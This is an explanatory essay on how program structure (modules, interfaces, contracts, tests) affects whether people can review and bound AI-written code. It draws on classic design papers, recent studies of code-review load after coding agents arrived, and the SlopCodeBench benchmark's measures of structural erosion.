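# Modularity, abstraction and testability in AI-written code: can people review it, and can its behaviour be bounded?

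## What are modularity, abstraction and testability, and how could they help people check AI-written code?

Modularity is the division of a program into parts that people can write, study and change one at a time. Abstraction means describing a part only by what its users need to know. Testability is how easily tests can reveal a part's faults by setting its inputs and checking its results. Software engineers worked out much of the theory behind these ideas in the 1970s and 1980s, for teams building programs too large for any one person to know in full.

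Modularity, abstraction and testability have a new use now that coding agents (AI systems that write, run and edit code over many steps) produce programs faster than people can read them. Someone still has to decide whether to run each program. Good structure might let that person decide after reading only a small part of the code. It might also let automated tools rule out some kinds of behaviour, so that nobody has to read the code to check for them.

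Many projects check code through pull requests. A pull request is a proposed change that its author submits for review before anyone merges it into the shared code base. The reviewer sees the lines that the change adds and removes. On the code-hosting site GitHub, reviewers can comment on particular lines, approve the change or request changes, and administrators can require approvals before a merge (GitHub, *Pull request reviews*). *What Will Replace Pull Requests?* (Treude and Baltes, 2026) lists five roles that a pull request combines: it groups changes for testing and merging, lets reviewers inspect them, records the reasons for them, shows who proposed and approved them, and gives outsiders a way to contribute. Program structure mostly affects the inspection. A reviewer can read five changed lines quickly, but their safety may depend on hundreds of unchanged lines elsewhere.

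### One program written two ways

The program below reads customer records, computes a monthly statement for each customer and emails it. It is a single function, which is a named piece of code that runs when other code calls it. The code is shortened and in near-English.

```
send_statements(month):
    open the customer file
    for each line in the file:
        split the line into name, email and purchases
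        if email is not blank:
            address = email
        total = 0
        for each purchase made in month:
            total = total + price + tax
        text = "Dear " + name + ", you owe " + total
        connect to the mail server
        send text to address
```

Suppose that the full version runs to 400 lines because it also handles discounts, refunds and tax rules. A reviewer wants to know whether it can send data to the wrong person. It can, because when a customer's email is blank, the program skips the line that sets `address`. The previous customer's email is still there, so that person receives somebody else's statement. This fault is fairly easy to spot in a dozen lines but much harder in 400, because any line could change `address` or `text` or send a second message, and the reviewer has to read them all to be sure that none does.

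The same program can also consist of four modules. A module is a part of a program that other parts use only through its interface, meaning the names, inputs and outputs of its operations. The code that carries out those operations is the module's implementation.

| Module | Interface | Implementation | Lines | What the reviewer must check |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Records | Returns customers, each with a name, email and purchases | Reads the file format | 120 | All three items come from the same record |
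| Statements | Takes a name, purchases and a month; returns text | Applies tax, discounts and layout | 220 | Nothing, if it does only what its interface shows |
| Mailer | Takes a text and an address; sends one message | Connects to the mail server | 50 | The message goes to that address and nowhere else |
| Run | Starts the monthly job | Calls the other three in order | 10 | Each statement goes out with the same customer's email |

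The core of Run fits in three lines:

```
for each customer in Records.customers():
    statement = Statements.compute(customer.name, customer.purchases, month)
    Mailer.send(statement, customer.email)
```

The reviewer has to read 180 lines instead of 400. Most of the reduction comes from skipping the charging rules, which are long and intricate but don't affect who receives what. A reviewer checking whether the totals are right would instead focus on Statements and could largely ignore Mailer.

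An interface specifies how to call a piece of code, but not what must hold before the code runs or what it then guarantees. Programmers can state these conditions in a contract. Meyer (1992), in *Applying "Design by Contract"*, explained the idea with a Paris courier. The customer supplies a package of at most five kilograms, with no side over two metres, and pays 100 francs; the courier delivers within four hours. In software, the customer's obligations become preconditions and the courier's become postconditions. For Mailer, the precondition could be that the address is not blank, and the postcondition that exactly one message has gone out, to that address. Contracts also help reviewers locate bugs. Meyer treats a broken precondition as a bug in the calling code, so if a blank address reaches Mailer, the reviewer should look in Run or Records.

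A test runs a piece of code on chosen inputs and compares the result with the expected one. The long function allows only an end-to-end test, which runs the whole program and checks its final output. To expose the address fault, the tester must prepare a customer file in which a blank email follows a filled one, set up a stand-in mail server, and check where each message went. With the modules, a local test can give Records two lines, the second without an email, and check that the second customer's email comes back blank. The tester needs no mail server and no knowledge of tax.

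### Where to cut

Splitting a program into pieces does not guarantee any of this. The computer scientist David Parnas made the classic argument about where to divide a program in *On the Criteria To Be Used in Decomposing Systems into Modules* (1972), which compared two designs for a keyword index program. The program takes a list of lines, such as book titles, and repeatedly moves the first word of each to the end, so that "Sense and Sensibility" also yields "and Sensibility Sense" and "Sensibility Sense and". It then prints all these "circular shifts" in alphabetical order, so a reader can find a title under any of its words.

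The first design follows a flowchart. It has separate modules for input, shifting, alphabetizing and output, which share tables in memory, and a master control that runs them in sequence. The second design starts from a list of design decisions that are difficult to make or likely to change, and each module hides one of them from the other modules. For example, a line-storage module has an operation that returns a given character of a given word in a given line, and no other module depends on how the characters are stored in memory. Parnas called this criterion "information hiding" and worked through five possible changes.

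| Decision that changes | Flowchart design | Information-hiding design |
|---|---|---|
| Format of the input | One module | One module |
| Keeping all lines in main memory | Every module | Line storage only |
| Packing four characters into each memory word | Every module | Line storage only |
| Keeping an index of the shifts instead of the shifts themselves | Shifter, alphabetizer and output | Shifter only |
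| Sorting the whole list once, in advance | Alphabetizer and output | Alphabetizer only |

Parnas thought even the better design had a fault. The shifter's interface fixed the order of the shifts, which its users did not need it to do, so it ruled out a version that generates them in alphabetical order from the start.

The customer program shows why the criterion matters for review. Its modules follow the steps of the work (read, compute, send), as a flowchart would, but they also hide the file format, the charging rules and the mail service. If Records instead left the raw lines in a shared table, and Mailer took each customer's email address from the third column, the program would still have four modules. But if someone then inserted a column for the account manager's email, Mailer could start sending customers' statements to account managers, even though nobody had changed Mailer.

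Parnas did not measure how much easier the second design is to understand. The index is small enough for a good programmer to write in a week or two, and he bases his claim that people can study its modules one at a time on "my subjective judgment". The table of changes is stronger evidence, because a reader can check each row against the designs.

Two terms from the same period describe how well a program has been divided. Coupling is the strength of the connections between modules, and cohesion is how closely the elements inside one module belong together. Stevens, Myers and Constantine (1974) defined both in *Structured design*, where they called cohesion "binding". Their scale of cohesion runs from coincidental, where lines share a module for no particular reason, to functional, where they all serve a single task. They noted that chopping up an existing program can produce coincidental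 cohesion, so telling someone to "make it modular" afterwards may achieve little. In *modular & legible software for AI (& human) coders*, the MIT computer scientist Daniel Jackson (2026) describes two related failures: "conflation", where one module serves several functions, and "fragmentation", where one function is spread over several modules.

Coupling grows especially fast when modules share data. If M modules can all use the same N variables, each variable connects every module to every other in both directions, so errors can spread along N × M × (M − 1) paths. Stevens and colleagues calculated 150 paths for three modules sharing 25 variables. The four modules of the customer program would have 120 if they shared ten. In one of their examples, which closely resembles the misdirected statement, a module that reads from a terminal takes the terminal's address from a shared variable. A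 second module changes that variable, and the program then reads from the wrong terminal. Their remedy was to pass the address as an input with every call, as Run does with `customer.email`.

### Reviewable code and bounded behaviour

A reviewer can safely skip the 220 lines of Statements only if they do nothing except turn purchases into text, and the interface alone cannot ensure that. In most common programming languages, any function can open a file or a network connection. Statements could read the whole customer file, keep one customer's purchases in memory and mix them into the next statement, or send mail of its own, and Run would look exactly the same. A reviewer who skips those lines trusts that the author kept to the design.

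Making code reviewable and bounding its behaviour are separate aims that need different means. Code is reviewable when a person can tell, in the time available, whether it does what it should, which depends on that person's skill and patience. Its behaviour is bounded when a mechanism blocks any effect outside a stated set, whatever the code contains. For example, a compiler, the program that translates source code into machine instructions, might reject any version of Statements that refers to the mail service, or an operating system might run Statements without network access.

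An interface that nothing enforces can help people review code, but it can't bound what the code does. It shows an honest author where to put things and a reviewer where to look. Parnas was clear that the modules were for people. The two versions of the index could be identical once assembled into a running program, since they differ only in how the text divides the work. Contracts also need enforcement to bound behaviour. Meyer let the programmer choose whether the machine monitors them during a run, and a contract that is neither monitored nor proved only documents what the code should do.

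Parnas wanted information hiding to be more than a convention. *Information distribution aspects of design methodology* (2016), a blog post on an earlier Parnas paper, quotes the advice that a programmer "should not possess information that he should not use". In 1971 a manager could arrange this by deciding who received which documents, but that is harder with an agent that can search the whole code base. The idea of having the programming language enforce boundaries between modules is nearly as old. Morris (1973), in *Protection in Programming Languages*, described language mechanisms that protect one subprogram from the malfunctioning of another. According to a 2016 blog post on that paper, they are attractive because they might let people prove things about one module without considering the rest of the system. Capabilities are another mechanism of this kind. They are unforgeable program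 values that code must hold to perform an effect such as sending mail.

Rules for the agents themselves divide in the same way. Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, loads instruction files at the start of each conversation but, according to its documentation, treats them as "context, not enforced configuration". To block an action whatever the agent decides, users need a hook, a check that runs before the agent uses a tool. GitHub enforces one such limit in review. According to its documentation, quoted in *Where Accountability Lives* (2026), GitHub's cloud agent "cannot approve or merge a pull request", and a human must do both for the agent's drafts.

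A bound covers only what somebody has stated. If Mailer can send only to addresses in the customer file, no stranger will receive a statement, but customer A may still receive customer B's. The Statements module can have no access to mail or files and still compute the wrong total. The bound does hold, though, even if the code is unreadable or the reviewer is tired. Someone still has to check that the mechanism enforcing it works.

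### When the author is a coding agent

This theory applies regardless of who or what writes the code, but review practices were designed for human authors. AI agents differ partly in volume. They were opening more than 17 million pull requests a month by June 2026, according to GitHub figures that Treude and Baltes cite. With so many changes to review, reducing the amount reviewers have to read becomes more valuable.

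Another difference concerns memory. Naur (1985), in *Programming as Theory Building*, argued that the main product of programming is knowledge in the programmers' heads, which he called a theory. Someone who has the theory can explain why each part of the program is what it is and how a new demand should fit in. Naur described a group that set out to extend another group's compiler, with full documentation, annotated code and personal advice from the original group. The documentation discussed the relevant facilities at length, but in several major cases the new group still proposed patches that would have destroyed the design's power and simplicity. The original group saw this at once. Later programmers worked without such advice, and after about ten years the old structure was still visible but had become useless.

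When an agent wrote the code, there may be no original author to ask. Anthropic explains that each Claude Code session begins with a fresh context window (the text the model can draw on at one time), and that only written notes carry knowledge from one session to the next. *Knowledge-Based Pull Requests* (2026) points out that a final code change usually leaves out which alternatives failed and which assumptions remained uncertain. For example, a reviewer who sees that Statements rounds each purchase instead of the total may have no way to learn whether a tax rule required this or the agent just happened to write it that way.

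Two recent papers draw opposite conclusions from this. *A Literate Programming Environment for Human and Machine Agents* (2026) says that, on Naur's view, the model cannot learn the theory, so building and carrying it remains entirely the human programmer's job. *Knowledge as Code* (2026) argues that because agents retain nothing between sessions, the theory has to be kept outside them, mainly in the code, where people can inspect and run it. The compiler story is evidence against this second position, since careful documentation was not enough there, but it is a single case about human teams. There is little direct evidence on agents. Of the 50 documents that Treude and Baltes reviewed, 22 described the loss of the prompts and decisions behind generated code as a problem, but none of the 22 tested whether saving them helps reviewers find defects. Information hiding preserves at least a little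 of the theory in the code, because a later reader can locate a decision by finding the module built around it.

A reviewer of human work can usually assume that the person who submitted a change understands it and can answer questions about it. The person who submits an agent's change may never have read it. In *Plausible Is Not Enough*, Rahman, Alam and colleagues (2026) asked 239 practitioners in 31 countries the same questions about human-authored and AI-authored pull requests. For human work, 28.5% said their own reasoning through the critical cases was sufficient evidence for approval, compared with 55.2% for AI work. The share who would block approval while some uncertainty remained was 19.4% for human work and 43.9% for AI work. These are self-reports, and respondents may behave differently under deadline.

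*Who Pays the Review Cost?* (Rahman, Alam and colleagues, 2026), a second paper on a survey of 239 practitioners, separates reviewability from correctness. A correct change can still be hard to review if it is poorly divided or comes without reasons, test evidence or someone accountable for it. Modules and local tests can supply the division and some of the evidence, but not a person who answers for the change. An enforced limit matters most when that person is missing, because it doesn't rely on the author's understanding. For example, if Statements has no access to mail, files or any memory of earlier customers, an agent can rewrite all 220 lines of it and the reviewer need not check again whether data could reach the wrong person.

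## Can people check AI-written code by reading it?

Reading works as a check only if people have time to read the code and notice its faults when they do. Company data show that reviewers are already short of time. In experiments with known faults, mostly in code written by people, readers missed many of the faults even when they had no other work waiting. There is little evidence on whether better structure helps readers find more faults, and the results are mixed.

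### More code than reviewers can absorb

The broadest data come from Jellyfish, a company that sells software for tracking engineering teams' work. Chen and Stratton (2026), in *Artificial Intelligence in the Firm*, used its records of code changes, tasks and calendar events to compare firms before and after they adopted AI coding tools. Because firms adopted at different times, they could use those that had not yet adopted, or never did, to estimate what would have happened without the tools. This method, called a staggered difference-in-differences design, gives the right answer only if adopters and the comparison firms would otherwise have followed similar paths. Chen and Stratton think this is plausible because security checks, legal approval and pilots take much longer at some firms than at others, for reasons that probably have little to do with growth.

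The paper's 14 November 2026 version covers 720,542 engineers at 655 firms, from January 2021 to August 2026. Woodruff (2026) sets out its main figures in *Code Review Is the Bottleneck. That's the Good News*. After a firm adopted coding agents, its lines of code rose by 44% and its pull requests by 35.7%. The time from submitting a pull request to getting approval rose by 56.1%, and comments per change rose by 38.6%. The number of resolved tasks rose by only 13.7%, a result the economists call borderline. An August version, with data only to March 2026, reported smaller increases in lines of code (30%) and pull requests (23%). It also found that reviewers sent back a larger share of changes for revision.

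These reviewers seem to have responded to the extra code by working harder. Chen and Stratton estimate that labour spent on coding fell by 22.7% while labour spent on review rose by 43.4%, and bug reports per developer did not change significantly. Woodruff had claimed a few days earlier that most teams end up approving code without properly checking it, but he withdrew the claim after reading the paper. He still cautioned that firms that pay for engineering analytics may be more disciplined than most, and that counting bug reports does not measure outages.

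Adding reviewers is hard because people review code best when they know the code around it. At these firms, someone already familiar with the code did 82.8% of reviews. A new colleague can't share the work until they have learned the code too. In *Writing Code vs. Shipping Code*, Demirer, Musolff and Yang (2026) reached a similar conclusion from data on software releases. They estimated the elasticity of substitution between AI and human effort at 0.25, which is far enough below 1 that more AI effort makes up for very little missing human effort.

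*AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) describes a company where human review could not keep up. In June 2025, the chief technology officer of a mid-sized software firm set engineers the goal of using AI to double their merged pull requests within a year. The researchers followed 802 developers and 196,212 pull requests from January 2024 to April 2026. Output per active developer did not reach double until the tenth month. The researchers attribute an increase of about 1.5 times to each developer's own use of AI. The rest of the increase occurred among both users and non-users of AI, so the researchers cannot tell how much of it AI caused.

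| | Before | April 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Pull requests per active developer per month | 21.2 | 44.3 |
| Lines in the median pull request | 35 | 61 |
| Share with at least one human review | 89% | 68% |
| Share with an automated AI review | about 19% | about 84% |
| Share with a written comment from a human reviewer | about 39% | about 21% |
| Share that a human approved without comment | about 50% | about 50% |

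The number of pull requests at the firm grew 3.1 times, while the number of people reviewing them grew 1.5 times. The median reviewer still commented in about three reviews a month, but gave roughly twice as many approvals without comment. A silent approval does not prove that nobody read the code, since a careful reader may have nothing to add. But if reviewers had read twice as many changes as closely as before, the number of reviews with comments would probably have grown too.

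The two studies conflict less than they seem to. He and colleagues also compared AI-labelled pull requests with others by the same author in the same month, adjusting for size. The AI-labelled ones drew about 9% more human comments and took about 20% longer to go from first human review to merge. In both datasets, AI-written code seems to take people longer to review. The company in the second study kept up by letting more of it skip human review, and late in the period it began to approve some changes automatically.

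### What a low revert rate leaves out

The share of reverts (changes that undo an earlier one) fell slightly across the company, and it did not rise for individual developers after they took up AI. One might expect it to rise if thinner review were letting much more bad code through. The researchers also found that developers did not open more bug fixes in the same repository within 7 or 14 days of merging an AI-labelled change. The researchers could not see whether a fix touched the same files.

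This is fair evidence against a sudden collapse in quality. It is much weaker evidence about faults that take time to show, because a revert happens only when somebody notices a problem and decides to undo the change instead of repairing it. In the customer program, the version that sends one customer's statement to another would count as a success until a recipient complained. A programmer might then add a line to fix it, and the revert count would still be zero. Revert counts also don't measure whether working code will be hard to change later.

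Reverts per developer rose by about 40% while pull requests per developer rose by about 80%, so the share of pull requests that were reverted fell by about a fifth. If each bad change does a fixed amount of harm, total harm rose even though the share fell. He and colleagues say they cannot rule out more defects, more incidents or less maintainable code.

### Less comment per line, with or without agents

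Reviewers of public code also comment less than they used to. *Comprehension Audits to Mitigate Risks from Automated AI Research* (2026) examined repositories from 224 organizations with AI projects. By June 2026, human reviewers' comments per thousand lines had fallen to 36% of their early-2024 rate on pull requests that used AI, and to 46% on those that did not. About 80% of the pull requests without AI still had a formal review by someone other than the author, and the share for those with AI was typically about eight percentage points lower.

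*Does Working with AI Agents Change How Developers Code, Test, and Review?* (Awan, 2026) followed 669 developers in 103 repositories before and after agents arrived. Their reviews became faster, less detailed and more permissive. But reviews by 228 developers in repositories without agent activity changed in the same way, so agents may not be the direct cause. Awan instead attributes the shift to wider trends in software development. The developers who worked with agents wrote much longer descriptions of their changes and tested slightly more.

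Surveys of developers suggest that reviewers are overloaded. *AI coding agents are reviewing their own code* (Kerner, 2026) reports a survey of 377 engineers and engineering leaders, of whom 45% called review capacity the biggest bottleneck in delivering software. Only 26% were very confident that they understood AI-written changes as thoroughly as human-written ones. A vendor of AI review tools sponsored the survey, so the results should be read with some caution. In *Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices* (2026), 79% of respondents used AI to understand pull requests or guide their review, but the survey did not support the idea that this removes the difficulty with volume.

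The pressure to read less is likely to grow. Woodruff describes a simulation by Chen and Stratton in which software output rises by 57.8% by 2031 if review continues at its present pace, and by 341.4% if review speeds up as fast as coding does. A firm could pursue the larger gain by making changes easier to read, or by approving them with less reading. Woodruff points out that a dashboard of approval times would look the same either way.

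### How long careful reading takes

Research on how fast people can review code predates AI-written code. Kemerer and Paulk (2009), in *The Impact of Design and Code Reviews on Software Quality*, analysed records from the Personal Software Process, a training method in which programmers review their own work and log each defect. They found that reviewing 200 lines an hour or less was effective, and that code reviews at that rate caught more than half of the defects.

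Cohen (2006), in *Best Kept Secrets of Peer Code Review*, drew more lenient guidelines from about 2,500 reviews at the network-equipment maker Cisco. Cohen recommended that reviewers stay below 300 to 500 lines an hour, take on at most 400 lines at a time, and stop after 60 to 90 minutes. Cohen's company sold a review tool. The Cisco records also include only the defects that reviewers reported, so we can't tell from them what share of the real defects anyone found.

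The table applies these rates to a 1,000-line change and to the customer program from the previous section, where good structure cut the number of lines a reviewer has to read from 400 to 180.

| Reading rate | 1,000-line change | Customer program, all 400 lines | Customer program, 180 lines |
|---|---|---|---|
| 200 lines an hour | 5 hours | 2 hours | 54 minutes |
| 300 lines an hour | 3 hours 20 minutes | 1 hour 20 minutes | 36 minutes |
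| 500 lines an hour | 2 hours | 48 minutes | 22 minutes |

With a limit of 400 lines per session, the 1,000-line change needs at least three sessions. Someone who reviews for two hours a day at 200 lines an hour finishes it in two and a half days. If the change contains ten defects and the reviewer does as well as the programmers Kemerer and Paulk studied, up to four will remain. Those programmers were reading their own small programs, and code written by a stranger or an agent may well take longer to review.

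At 200 lines an hour, the time needed to read the median pull request at the company that He and colleagues studied rose from about 10 minutes to about 18. Each reviewer also had twice as many pull requests to read. If the medians are a fair guide to the whole load, careful reading would have taken each reviewer about three and a half times as long as before. Few people could do that without giving up most of their other work, so the silent approvals are not surprising.

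These rates count only the changed lines, so looking up the unchanged code that a change depends on takes extra time.

### What readers find when they do read

For *An Empirical Study on the Effectiveness of Security Code Review* (2013), Edmundson and colleagues hired 30 developers to review a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities. None found all seven, and more experienced developers were not reliably more effective. Those who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more false ones, so some of their apparent skill may have been a greater willingness to flag possible problems.

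Readers can miss even a common, well-documented kind of fault. In *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, Braz, Fregnan and colleagues (2021) gave 146 people a code change that failed to check incoming data properly. Of these, 105 had at least three years of professional experience. Many who missed the fault at first found it once the researchers warned them it was there, but 60 participants (41%) still missed it.

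What reviewers are looking for strongly affects what they find. In a later experiment with 150 participants, *Less is More* (2022), Braz and colleagues found that asking people to focus on security made them eight times as likely to detect a vulnerability. Adding a security checklist, even one tailored to the change, brought no significant further improvement. A reviewer who is thinking about whether a feature works may therefore overlook a security fault that the same person could find under different instructions. It is hard to give a single detection rate for human review because the rate depends on the fault, the code and what the reviewer is looking for.

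A few experiments have used AI-written code. In *Developer Behaviors in Validating and Repairing LLM-Generated Code Using IDE and Eye Tracking* (Tang et al., 2024), 28 people checked and repaired code from GitHub's Copilot assistant. Those who knew that an AI had written it searched more and performed better, but also had a higher mental workload. *LLM Critics Help Catch LLM Bugs* (McAleese et al., 2024), a study from OpenAI, compared human and AI reviewers on code from ChatGPT. The AI reviewers caught more bugs than contractors the company paid to review code. Teams of people and AI caught about as many bugs as the AI alone and reported fewer problems that did not exist.

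AI help can also narrow what people look at. In *Deep Learning-based Code Reviews*, Tufano and colleagues (2025) recorded over 50 hours of 29 experts reviewing programs, with and without an AI-generated review to start from. Those who started from the AI's review concentrated on the places it flagged. They found more minor problems but no additional serious ones, saved no time and felt no more confident. None of these experiments tested a large change from a current coding agent, which is now the most important case. Newer models may leave fewer simple mistakes, and the remaining mistakes could be harder for people to spot.

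*The End of Code Review* (2026) argues that human review has become redundant because coding agents can meet all the stated goals of review, including finding defects and spreading knowledge in a team, at lower cost. It also argues that firms cannot keep requiring people to inspect the code that agents write. The OpenAI result supports the claim about finding defects, at least in comparison with paid contractors. Tufano's experiment does not contradict that claim, because it tested people working from an AI review and not AI review alone.

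The case for removing people from review altogether is weaker. In the survey that Kerner reports, 47% of respondents said their organizations rely on coding agents to review code that the same agents wrote, and an agent may well miss the same fault twice. He et al. note that researchers are only beginning to evaluate the automated reviewers that replace people. Better automated review also would not provide a person who can be held accountable for the code.

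### Does better structure help reviewers find more?

Structure could let people skip code that is irrelevant to their question, as in the customer program, where the reviewer skipped 220 lines. It could also help them notice more in the code they do read. Experiments have mostly tested the second effect, and the results are less encouraging than you would expect from the design theory of the 1970s.

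The most direct test, *The Effects of Change Decomposition on Code Review* (Di Biase, Bruntink and colleagues, 2019), examined whether splitting up a change helps reviewers. Twenty-eight developers, some professionals and some graduate students, reviewed either a single pull request that mixed separate concerns or the same work split into coherent pull requests. The two groups did not differ in how many defects they found or in how well they understood the reasons for the change, but those with the split version reported fewer false problems and looked up more of the surrounding context.

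This null result matters because it goes against common advice, but the experiment was small. With two groups of about 14, a study has an 80% chance of detecting a difference only if it is at least about one standard deviation, which is large, so the experiment could have missed a moderate gain from splitting. The drop in false alarms is also a benefit, since each one takes up the author's and reviewer's time. The experiment also divided only the change under review, and a well-divided pull request can still modify a tangled code base.

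In *Associating Working Memory Capacity and Code Change Ordering with Code Review Performance* (Baum, Schneider and Bacchelli, 2019), 50 people, mostly professional developers, looked for seeded defects in one small change and two larger ones. They were significantly more effective on the small change. This is compatible with di Biase's result, because a small change is less work to review, whereas splitting a large change leaves the same total amount to read. Keeping pull requests small may therefore do little to help people review an agent's output if the agent submits more of them.

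The same experiment provides indirect evidence that a program's internal structure matters to reviewers. Some defects are delocalized, meaning that a reader can recognize them only by combining information from different places in the code. People with a larger working memory, the ability to hold several things in mind at once, tended to find more of these defects, but there was almost no such link for other defects. The address fault in the 400-line customer function could well be delocalized, whereas in the modular version it would be contained within Records.

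That suggests dividing a program into modules helps when it brings together the facts a reader needs to compare, and could make review harder when it scatters them. But Baum and colleagues did not vary the program's structure, so this is an inference from their result. They also tested whether presenting the parts of a change in a better order made review more efficient, but could not reach a reliable conclusion.

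Reviewers can be less likely to find some faults when the files containing them appear later in a review. In *First Come First Served*, Fregnan, Braz and colleagues (2022) seeded two defects in two files and switched the files' positions between groups, with 106 participants in all. Position made no difference for one defect, but the odds of finding the other were 64% lower when its file came last. In 219,476 real pull requests, files that appeared earlier also received more comments. Review tools usually sort files alphabetically, so a file may get more attention because of its name. If a design puts the riskiest code in a few known files, a team could show those files first, though the experiment did not test this approach.

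The evidence is clearer that descriptive variable names make code quicker to check. Hofmeister, Siegmund and Holt (2017), in *Shorter Identifier Names Take Longer to Comprehend*, timed 72 professional developers as they searched short pieces of code for defects. The variables were named with full words, abbreviations or single letters, and developers were 19% faster on average with full words. If the effect carried over to large changes, it would be a modest saving, cutting a five-hour review to a little over four hours.

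Abbes and colleagues (2011) came closer to varying modularity in *An Empirical Study of the Impact of Two Antipatterns, Blob and Spaghetti Code, on Program Comprehension*. A Blob is one large class, or program unit, that does much of the system's work. Spaghetti code has little structure. In three experiments with 24 people each, neither antipattern alone significantly reduced performance on comprehension tasks, but the two together did. Participants answered questions about the code rather than looking for defects, so the result applies to review only if people who understand code better also find more of its defects.

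None of this shows that modular code makes reviewers find more faults per line they read. The experiments are small, several measure something related to the question but not the question itself, and most used changes that people could finish in one session. An effect might appear only in programs too large for one person to keep in mind, which are the programs modularity was meant for. For now, the stronger argument for structure is that it can reduce how much people must read. The drop from two hours to 54 minutes in the customer program is possible without anyone getting better at spotting faults, as long as the lines they skip cannot affect the answer.

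### Readable code is also easier to accept

Reviewers like structured code, whether or not it helps them detect faults. In *Human Reviewers' Attitudes Toward LLM-generated Security Patches*, Iannone, Camporese and colleagues (2026) recruited 111 master's students and 14 professionals, and analysed valid responses from 93 of them. Each participant saw four real vulnerabilities in open-source Java projects, with two patches (small changes that repair a fault) for each. GPT-4o wrote one patch and Claude 3.7 Sonnet wrote the other. Both are early models by today's standards. Participants rated both patches, chose one and explained why.

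The researchers then told participants that a person had written one of the two patches and an AI the other, although AI had written both, and let them choose again. Participants switched in 32 of 186 cases (17%) when told that their chosen patch was the AI's, compared with 12 of 186 (6%) when told it was the human's. The students accounted for the whole difference. Professionals switched in 2 of 28 cases under either label, but there were only 14 of them, so the experiment could easily have missed a bias.

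The experiment measured which patches participants preferred. It could not show whether they would catch a faulty patch, because there were none. All the patches passed the relevant tests, and the researchers had also checked by hand that they could fix the vulnerability without changing the program's other behaviour. A participant who switched because of a label was influenced by something irrelevant in this case, but did not accept a faulty patch.

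Participants mentioned security in 45% of their explanations and ease of understanding in 36%. Maintainability came up in 20%, most often because a patch put particular tasks into separate functions. At the end, 86% of participants said overall readability had influenced their decisions, compared with 43% for the number of lines changed. A few said they were torn between a clearer patch and one that seemed safer. In the quoted examples, they chose the one that seemed safer.

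People were more likely to choose a fix they understood. Participants rated how well they understood the way each patch removed the vulnerability, on a five-point scale. When they rated one patch a point higher than the other, the odds of choosing it rose about 2.5 times. Professionals mentioned ease of understanding more often than security (43% of explanations against 27%). Iannone and colleagues suggest that the professionals may have taken correctness for granted because they knew the patches had passed their tests. That would be risky in ordinary review, where a patch can pass its tests and still be wrong.

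It makes sense to prefer a patch that one can understand, because it is easier to check. But clarity alone does not show that code is safe. Authors can make harmful code look harmless, and a reviewer with 18 minutes for a change may trust a tidy layout instead of doing checks they have no time for.

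## Does AI-written code stay well structured when the AI chooses the structure?

Coding agents that aren't told how to divide a program usually let complexity build up in a few large functions, and the problem tends to get worse as they extend their own code. Instructions and automatic feedback can reduce this buildup, at least on the usual measures, which cover only part of what a reviewer needs to know.

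Most coding benchmarks (standard sets of tasks for comparing AI systems) cannot show how agents structure code over time. The agent typically fixes one fault in a project whose modules people have already chosen, and the task ends there. *SlopCodeBench* (Orlanski, Roy and colleagues, 2025) introduces a benchmark in which agents have to keep extending code they designed themselves.

### How SlopCodeBench works

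Each problem is a series of specifications called checkpoints. The agent writes a program from scratch at the first checkpoint and extends it to meet new requirements at each later one. The current release has 36 problems with three to eight checkpoints each, for a total of 196 checkpoints. The specifications describe only the program's external behaviour, such as its commands, inputs and output format, so the agent chooses the functions, files and modules. The agent sees some examples but not the tests, which run the whole program and check only its output. Each checkpoint starts a new session, so the agent has to work out its earlier design decisions mainly from the code.

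One of the problems is to build a code-search tool. The first checkpoint requires a program that searches Python files for exact text or regular expressions, a notation for text patterns. The second adds JavaScript and C++. The third adds patterns with placeholders, where `$X` stands for any single code element, such as a variable or function call. Later checkpoints add automatic fixes and more languages. The table sketches how two possible designs would handle these changes.

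| New requirement | One search function with a branch for each case | A separate matcher for each kind of rule |
|---|---|---|
| Exact text and regular expressions | Write the function | Write two matchers with the same interface |
| JavaScript and C++ | Add language checks inside the function | Extend the list of languages |
| Patterns with placeholders | Add parsing and a second kind of search to the same function | Add a third matcher |
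| Automatic fixes | Rework the function so that other code can edit its matches | Add a module that takes matches from any matcher |

Both designs pass the first checkpoint, and the single function is quicker to write. It becomes harder to work with at the third, because finding whole code elements requires parsing each file into a tree instead of scanning its text. One agent's solution ended up close to the design in the middle column. By the fifth checkpoint, its function `find_matches_in_file()` was 117 lines long, contained nearly all of the program's branching, and checked the rule's type in more than one place.

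### Erosion and verbosity

The benchmark's main structural measure, erosion, is the share of a program's complexity in its most complex functions. It is based on cyclomatic complexity, which is the number of independent paths through a function. This equals the number of branches plus one. The short version of `send_statements` in the first section has three branches (the loop over lines, the loop over purchases and the check for a blank email), so its complexity is 4.

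Each function then gets a "mass":

```
mass    = complexity × square root of the number of lines
erosion = mass of functions with complexity above 10 ÷ mass of all functions
```

Because of the square root, a function that is four times as long has only twice the mass. Here is the calculation for a program with three functions:

| Function | Complexity | Lines | Mass | Complexity above 10? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
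| A | 4 | 16 | 4 × 4 = 16 | No |
| B | 12 | 100 | 12 × 10 = 120 | Yes |
| C | 5 | 25 | 5 × 5 = 25 | No |

The total mass is 161 and B accounts for 120 of it, so erosion is 120/161, or about 0.75.

Verbosity is the share of lines that either duplicate the structure of other lines or match a list of wasteful patterns. Snorkel AI's *SlopCode Bench* page, the public home of the benchmark, lists 205 distinct rules for such patterns. One of them flags code that converts data to text and straight back again just to copy it. (Snorkel AI is a data company that helped fund the benchmark.)

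### What the agents produced

None of the 15 coding agents tested solved any problem from start to finish. The best, OpenAI's GPT-5.5, solved 14.8% of checkpoints under a strict rule that counts a checkpoint only if the agent has also solved all the earlier ones. An agent that solved only the first checkpoint of every problem would score higher, at 18.4%. GPT-5.5 passed the core tests at 66.8% of checkpoints, so its programs often did their main job but failed other requirements.

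Erosion rose in 77% of runs and verbosity in 75.5%. The average number of highly complex functions in a program grew from 3.6 to 23.7. In one problem, Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.7 wrote a command-line tool whose `main()` function grew from 38 lines to 240 over eight checkpoints, while its complexity rose from 13 to 92. The first version used a standard library to read the user's options, but the last used its own code, with two nearly identical branches for each of seven options. The agent never moved the repeated logic into a separate function.

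Copying also explains most of the growth in verbosity. Structural duplication grew by 96% over the runs, while the density of wasteful patterns barely changed. Duplicates give reviewers more to read, and someone who finds a fault in one copy has to look for the other copies.

For comparison, the researchers measured 473 open-source Python repositories, sampling up to 30 commits (saved changes) from the history of each.

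| | Agents | Human repositories |
|---|---|---|
| Average erosion | 0.68 | 0.34 |
| Average verbosity | 0.44 | 0.19 |
| Share in which erosion rose | 77% | 53% |
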